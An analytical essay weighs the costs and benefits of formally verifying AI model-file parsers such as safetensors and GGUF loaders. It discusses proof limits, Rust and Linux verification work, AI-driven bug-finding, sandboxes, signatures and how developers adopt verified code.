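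The theorems are much weaker than those about EverParse's parsers. A version of cJSON that read every number as 0 would never crash, so it would pass unless the test checked the values. The theorems also don't specify which entry a parser should keep when a safetensors header contains the same tensor name twice. But because the fuzz tests existed beforehand, a model has little room to weaken the statement it has to prove.

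Fuller proofs are possible where a good standard exists. Claude also proved that the Linux kernel's zlib code follows the format's published standard, and it wrote a verified interpreter for part of Python. That interpreter behaved the same as CPython, the usual interpreter, on 99.95% of more than 1.7 million random programs. Developers could check a GGUF specification in the same way, by comparing the verified parser with llama.cpp on millions of generated files.

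### Processors and threads

The proofs cover programs compiled for RISC-V, a processor design that few AI servers use. Each program has one thread, a fixed amount of memory and all its libraries built in. Leip (2026) points out in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* that Anthropic acknowledges that "most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM". A proof about the RISC-V program is still good evidence about the C source, since most overflows would occur on any processor. But it doesn't cover the compiler's output for x86, or code that only the x86 version uses.

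Leip's team at the security company Zellic began working on x86 in mid-September 2026 and had published a proof about a complete Linux program by the end of October. The standard C library makes such work harder on x86 because it chooses heavily optimized code for each processor. The team had to verify a string-comparison function with 316 instructions and 45 jumps, compared with 14 instructions and 4 jumps for the equivalent in Anthropic's setting. The x86 proof also assumes the exact processor model of the team's test machine, so it is an early step that a project could not yet adopt.

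The restriction to RISC-V looks temporary. In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) have already proved security properties of unmodified ARM machine code from Signal, the encrypted messenger. Their agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof, which depend on about 26,000 lines of specifications and processor rules that people must trust.

The restriction to one thread is a bigger problem for inference servers. Proving a single-threaded program correct would not reveal the two flaws in llama.cpp's server that depend on request timing.

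### What 64 MB means for a checkpoint

Anthropic's theorems apply to inputs smaller than 64 MB. That is enough for almost any configuration file, chat template or text request, and for most tokenizer files, but not for a checkpoint. At two bytes per weight, 64 MB holds 32 million weights, while a model with eight billion weights needs a 16 GB file, which is 250 times the limit.

The 64 MB limit matters less than this comparison suggests, because a small malicious file can declare huge sizes. The safetensors header that declared a tensor of 2^64 bytes needed no tensor data. Trying to prove a theorem about files below that limit would have exposed the bug, since Rust stops the program when it tries to read the missing data. The files behind the Ollama leak, which declared oversized tensors, could also be small.

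Other flaws appear only in large files. In llama.cpp's vocabulary code, a token's length turned negative once it reached 2^31 bytes. If the loader checks that the file contains the token's full text, an attacker needs a file of more than 2 GB to trigger the overflow. Every file below 64 MB would load safely, so the theorem, which covers only those files, could be true despite the flaw.

Developers could get around this limit the same way as 3D's 32-bit limit, by giving the test program only the safetensors header and the size of the whole file. The theorem would then cover files of any size. The official library accepts headers of up to 100 MB, so its developers would have to lower that maximum to just below 64 MB or extend the proof. GGUF's metadata is also usually far smaller than 64 MB, even with a large vocabulary. The code that later reads the weights would need a separate argument,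 for example that it reads only within the ranges the header parser approved.

### A proof about Rust code in Linux

Android apps communicate with system services through Binder, whose driver in the Linux kernel reads bytes that any app can choose. Developers have rewritten the driver in Rust, which removes most memory errors, but a panic could still bring down the kernel. *Verifying Linux's Rust Code* (Klaus, 2026) describes a proof that Binder's deserializer never panics and that it returns either a valid object or an error code for every input.

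Klaus's team at the company Runtime Verification first asked the driver's maintainer which properties were worth proving. The maintainer answered that the code must not panic on any input and that the driver must later clean up exactly the objects it has translated. The team then used existing tools to convert the Rust code into Lean, where AI provers did as much of the proof as they could.

The conversion failed in one place, where the driver stores different kinds of object in the same 40 bytes and uses a tag to tell them apart. The tools don't support this, so the team replaced it with a plain array of 40 bytes and functions that read each field at a fixed position. Checks during compilation ensure that the positions and sizes match those in the real kernel. The proof therefore covers a slightly altered copy of the code. It also assumes one fact about the sizes of types and leaves out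 the second property, which involves a larger part of the driver.

To see whether the approach would work elsewhere, the team ran the first conversion tool on all 92,000 lines of Rust in the kernel. No language feature caused a failure. Of the 28 larger components that failed, 27 failed because the tool lacked a model of the same shared kernel code. Somebody would have to write that model only once.

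This work is a closer precedent for safetensors than Hyper-V is, because the official safetensors library is also Rust code that reads untrusted bytes. A team could try to prove that the library never panics and that every tensor it accepts lies inside the file. The library would not change, so existing models would still load. The proof would also have to cover the code that parses the JSON header, or assume that this code works.

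### Is it the right code to verify?

Loaders resemble the code people have chosen to verify so far. They are small compared with the programs around them, and strangers supply their input. "Parsing untrusted bytes is historically where kernels get hurt", Klaus writes, and the recorded flaws in GGUF loaders suggest the same is true of AI software.

Nethermind's *Formal Verification and the Economics of Correctness* is more skeptical, although the company does verification itself. It calls the method "not economical in most contexts" but makes an exception for infrastructure that many other systems depend on. llama.cpp's loader fits that exception because a flaw in it also affects other products that use the same code. The owner of a custom loader inside one company's tool would do better to switch to a maintained library rather than verify it.

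### Does cheap bug-finding help or hurt the case?

AI now finds parser bugs quickly. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) reports that language models' scores on CyberGym, a benchmark for finding vulnerabilities, rose from under 20% at the start of 2025 to over 85% in 2026. The company concludes from such progress that "the standard defenses against cyberattacks are no longer sufficient". Anthropic has an interest in this conclusion because it sells the model that wrote its proofs, but the advisory on GGUF readers supports the point. An AI agent found six weaknesses in the readers and published them the same day.

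Defenders can use AI to find bugs too, and a proof would add little if AI found nearly every bug and developers fixed them. So far, however, people can't keep up with the reports. Anthropic's scans produced more than 29,000 candidate vulnerabilities in six months, and reviewers had checked about 6,000. By November 2, 2026, Anthropic had disclosed 5,087 vulnerabilities to open-source projects and knew of patches for 629, about one in eight. That share will probably rise, because some of the reports were recent.

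A proof can rule out a whole class of such bugs at once. But a project like llama.cpp, which already struggles with its bug reports, would also have to maintain the proof.

Nobody knows what it would cost to rely on patches alone. *Patching all security relevant open source software* roughly estimates the cost for the software that the internet depends on, with a median of about $1.9 billion and a range from $31 million to $168 billion. That range is too wide to show whether proofs would be cheaper.

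### How much is left to gain for safetensors?

The case for a new verified parser is weakest for Safetensors. Its library is already short and written in Rust, and auditors found no high-severity flaws in it. A replacement would mainly prevent panics and cases where loaders handle the same file differently, but it might reject files that work today. Proving the existing library panic-free, as Klaus's team did for Binder, would give part of that benefit with much less risk.

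Verification would help GGUF more, because llama.cpp's loader is in C++, where the same arithmetic mistakes corrupt memory. Rewriting that loader in Rust would remove much of the danger without any proof, but not all of it. Ollama's loader was in Go, which is also memory-safe, and Ollama still leaked memory contents. A proof that every accepted tensor lies inside the file would address both the corruption and the leak.

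### Attacks that need no parsing error

The best argument against spending much on verified loaders is that real attackers have had little need for parsing bugs. The malicious models found on Hugging Face used pickle's function calls, Python code named in the configuration file, or instructions in chat templates. Tolmach and Klaus write that "a valid proof of the wrong property is still the wrong result," and that applies here because a verified parser would accept nearly all of these models.

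This is a reason to deal with executable content first, especially where the fix is as simple as no longer using pickle for messages between servers. But parsing flaws can still be exploited, as in the Ollama leak, which needed no executable content. Attackers choose the easiest method that works, so memory errors in loaders become more attractive as weights-only loading and safetensors block easier attacks.

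### Changing formats

Model formats change, and each change can invalidate a proof. This is a minor problem for safetensors, whose layout is very simple, but it matters for GGUF, which gains new quantization types. To add a type to a generated parser, a developer adds its type code and size to the specification and reruns the generator. EverParse generates the parsers for all of Hyper-V's network formats in under two minutes.

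Proofs about compiled programs are more fragile because they refer to exact machine instructions, which a new compiler version can change even if the source code stays the same. llama.cpp went through more than 4,000 build numbers between its fixes for two flaws disclosed in 2026. If Claude can redo a proof in hours, developers could repeat it for each important release, but if it takes weeks, users will mostly run versions without a proof. One of the Linux developers who advised on Binder asked whether the conversion to Lean could be kept up to date instead of done once.

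### Sandboxes and signatures

A sandbox restricts what a program can do after an attacker takes it over. It needs no format specification and works against malicious pickles, faulty image decoders and bugs that use freed memory, so it covers more attacks than a verified parser and usually costs less. But it protects only what is outside it. The data that Ollama leaked was in the server's own memory, so a sandbox around the whole server would not have prevented the leak unless it also blocked the upload. Loading each model in a separate process would help, but the server would then have to read that process's output safely.

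Signatures address a different danger by letting a user detect that somebody has altered a file since its publisher signed it, such as by swapping two tokens in the vocabulary. They would not have stopped the two accounts that uploaded malicious GGUF models, because both could have signed their own files. Software also often fails to check signatures that exist. In *Package managers have an integrity problem*, Ryan (2026) tested 25 popular package managers, which download and install software libraries, and found that only two verified the integrity of every package they downloaded.

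### Getting developers to use verified code

*How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* gives three reasons why verification is rare: the tools may not exist, they are costly to use, and people may not adopt the verified code. AI has helped most with cost, by making proofs cheaper to write. It has helped less with adoption, which depends on whether a project's maintainers want the new code and can look after it.

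Microsoft's networking team accepted verified parsers because they broke nothing and met a strict performance limit. An open-source project would probably set similar conditions, and its volunteers might refuse a build that requires F* or Rocq. The project could avoid that dependency by storing the generated C or Rust in its repository and running the proof tools only when the format changes. Proving the existing code requires even less of the volunteers, because an outside team can do the work and send ordinary patches for any problems it finds.
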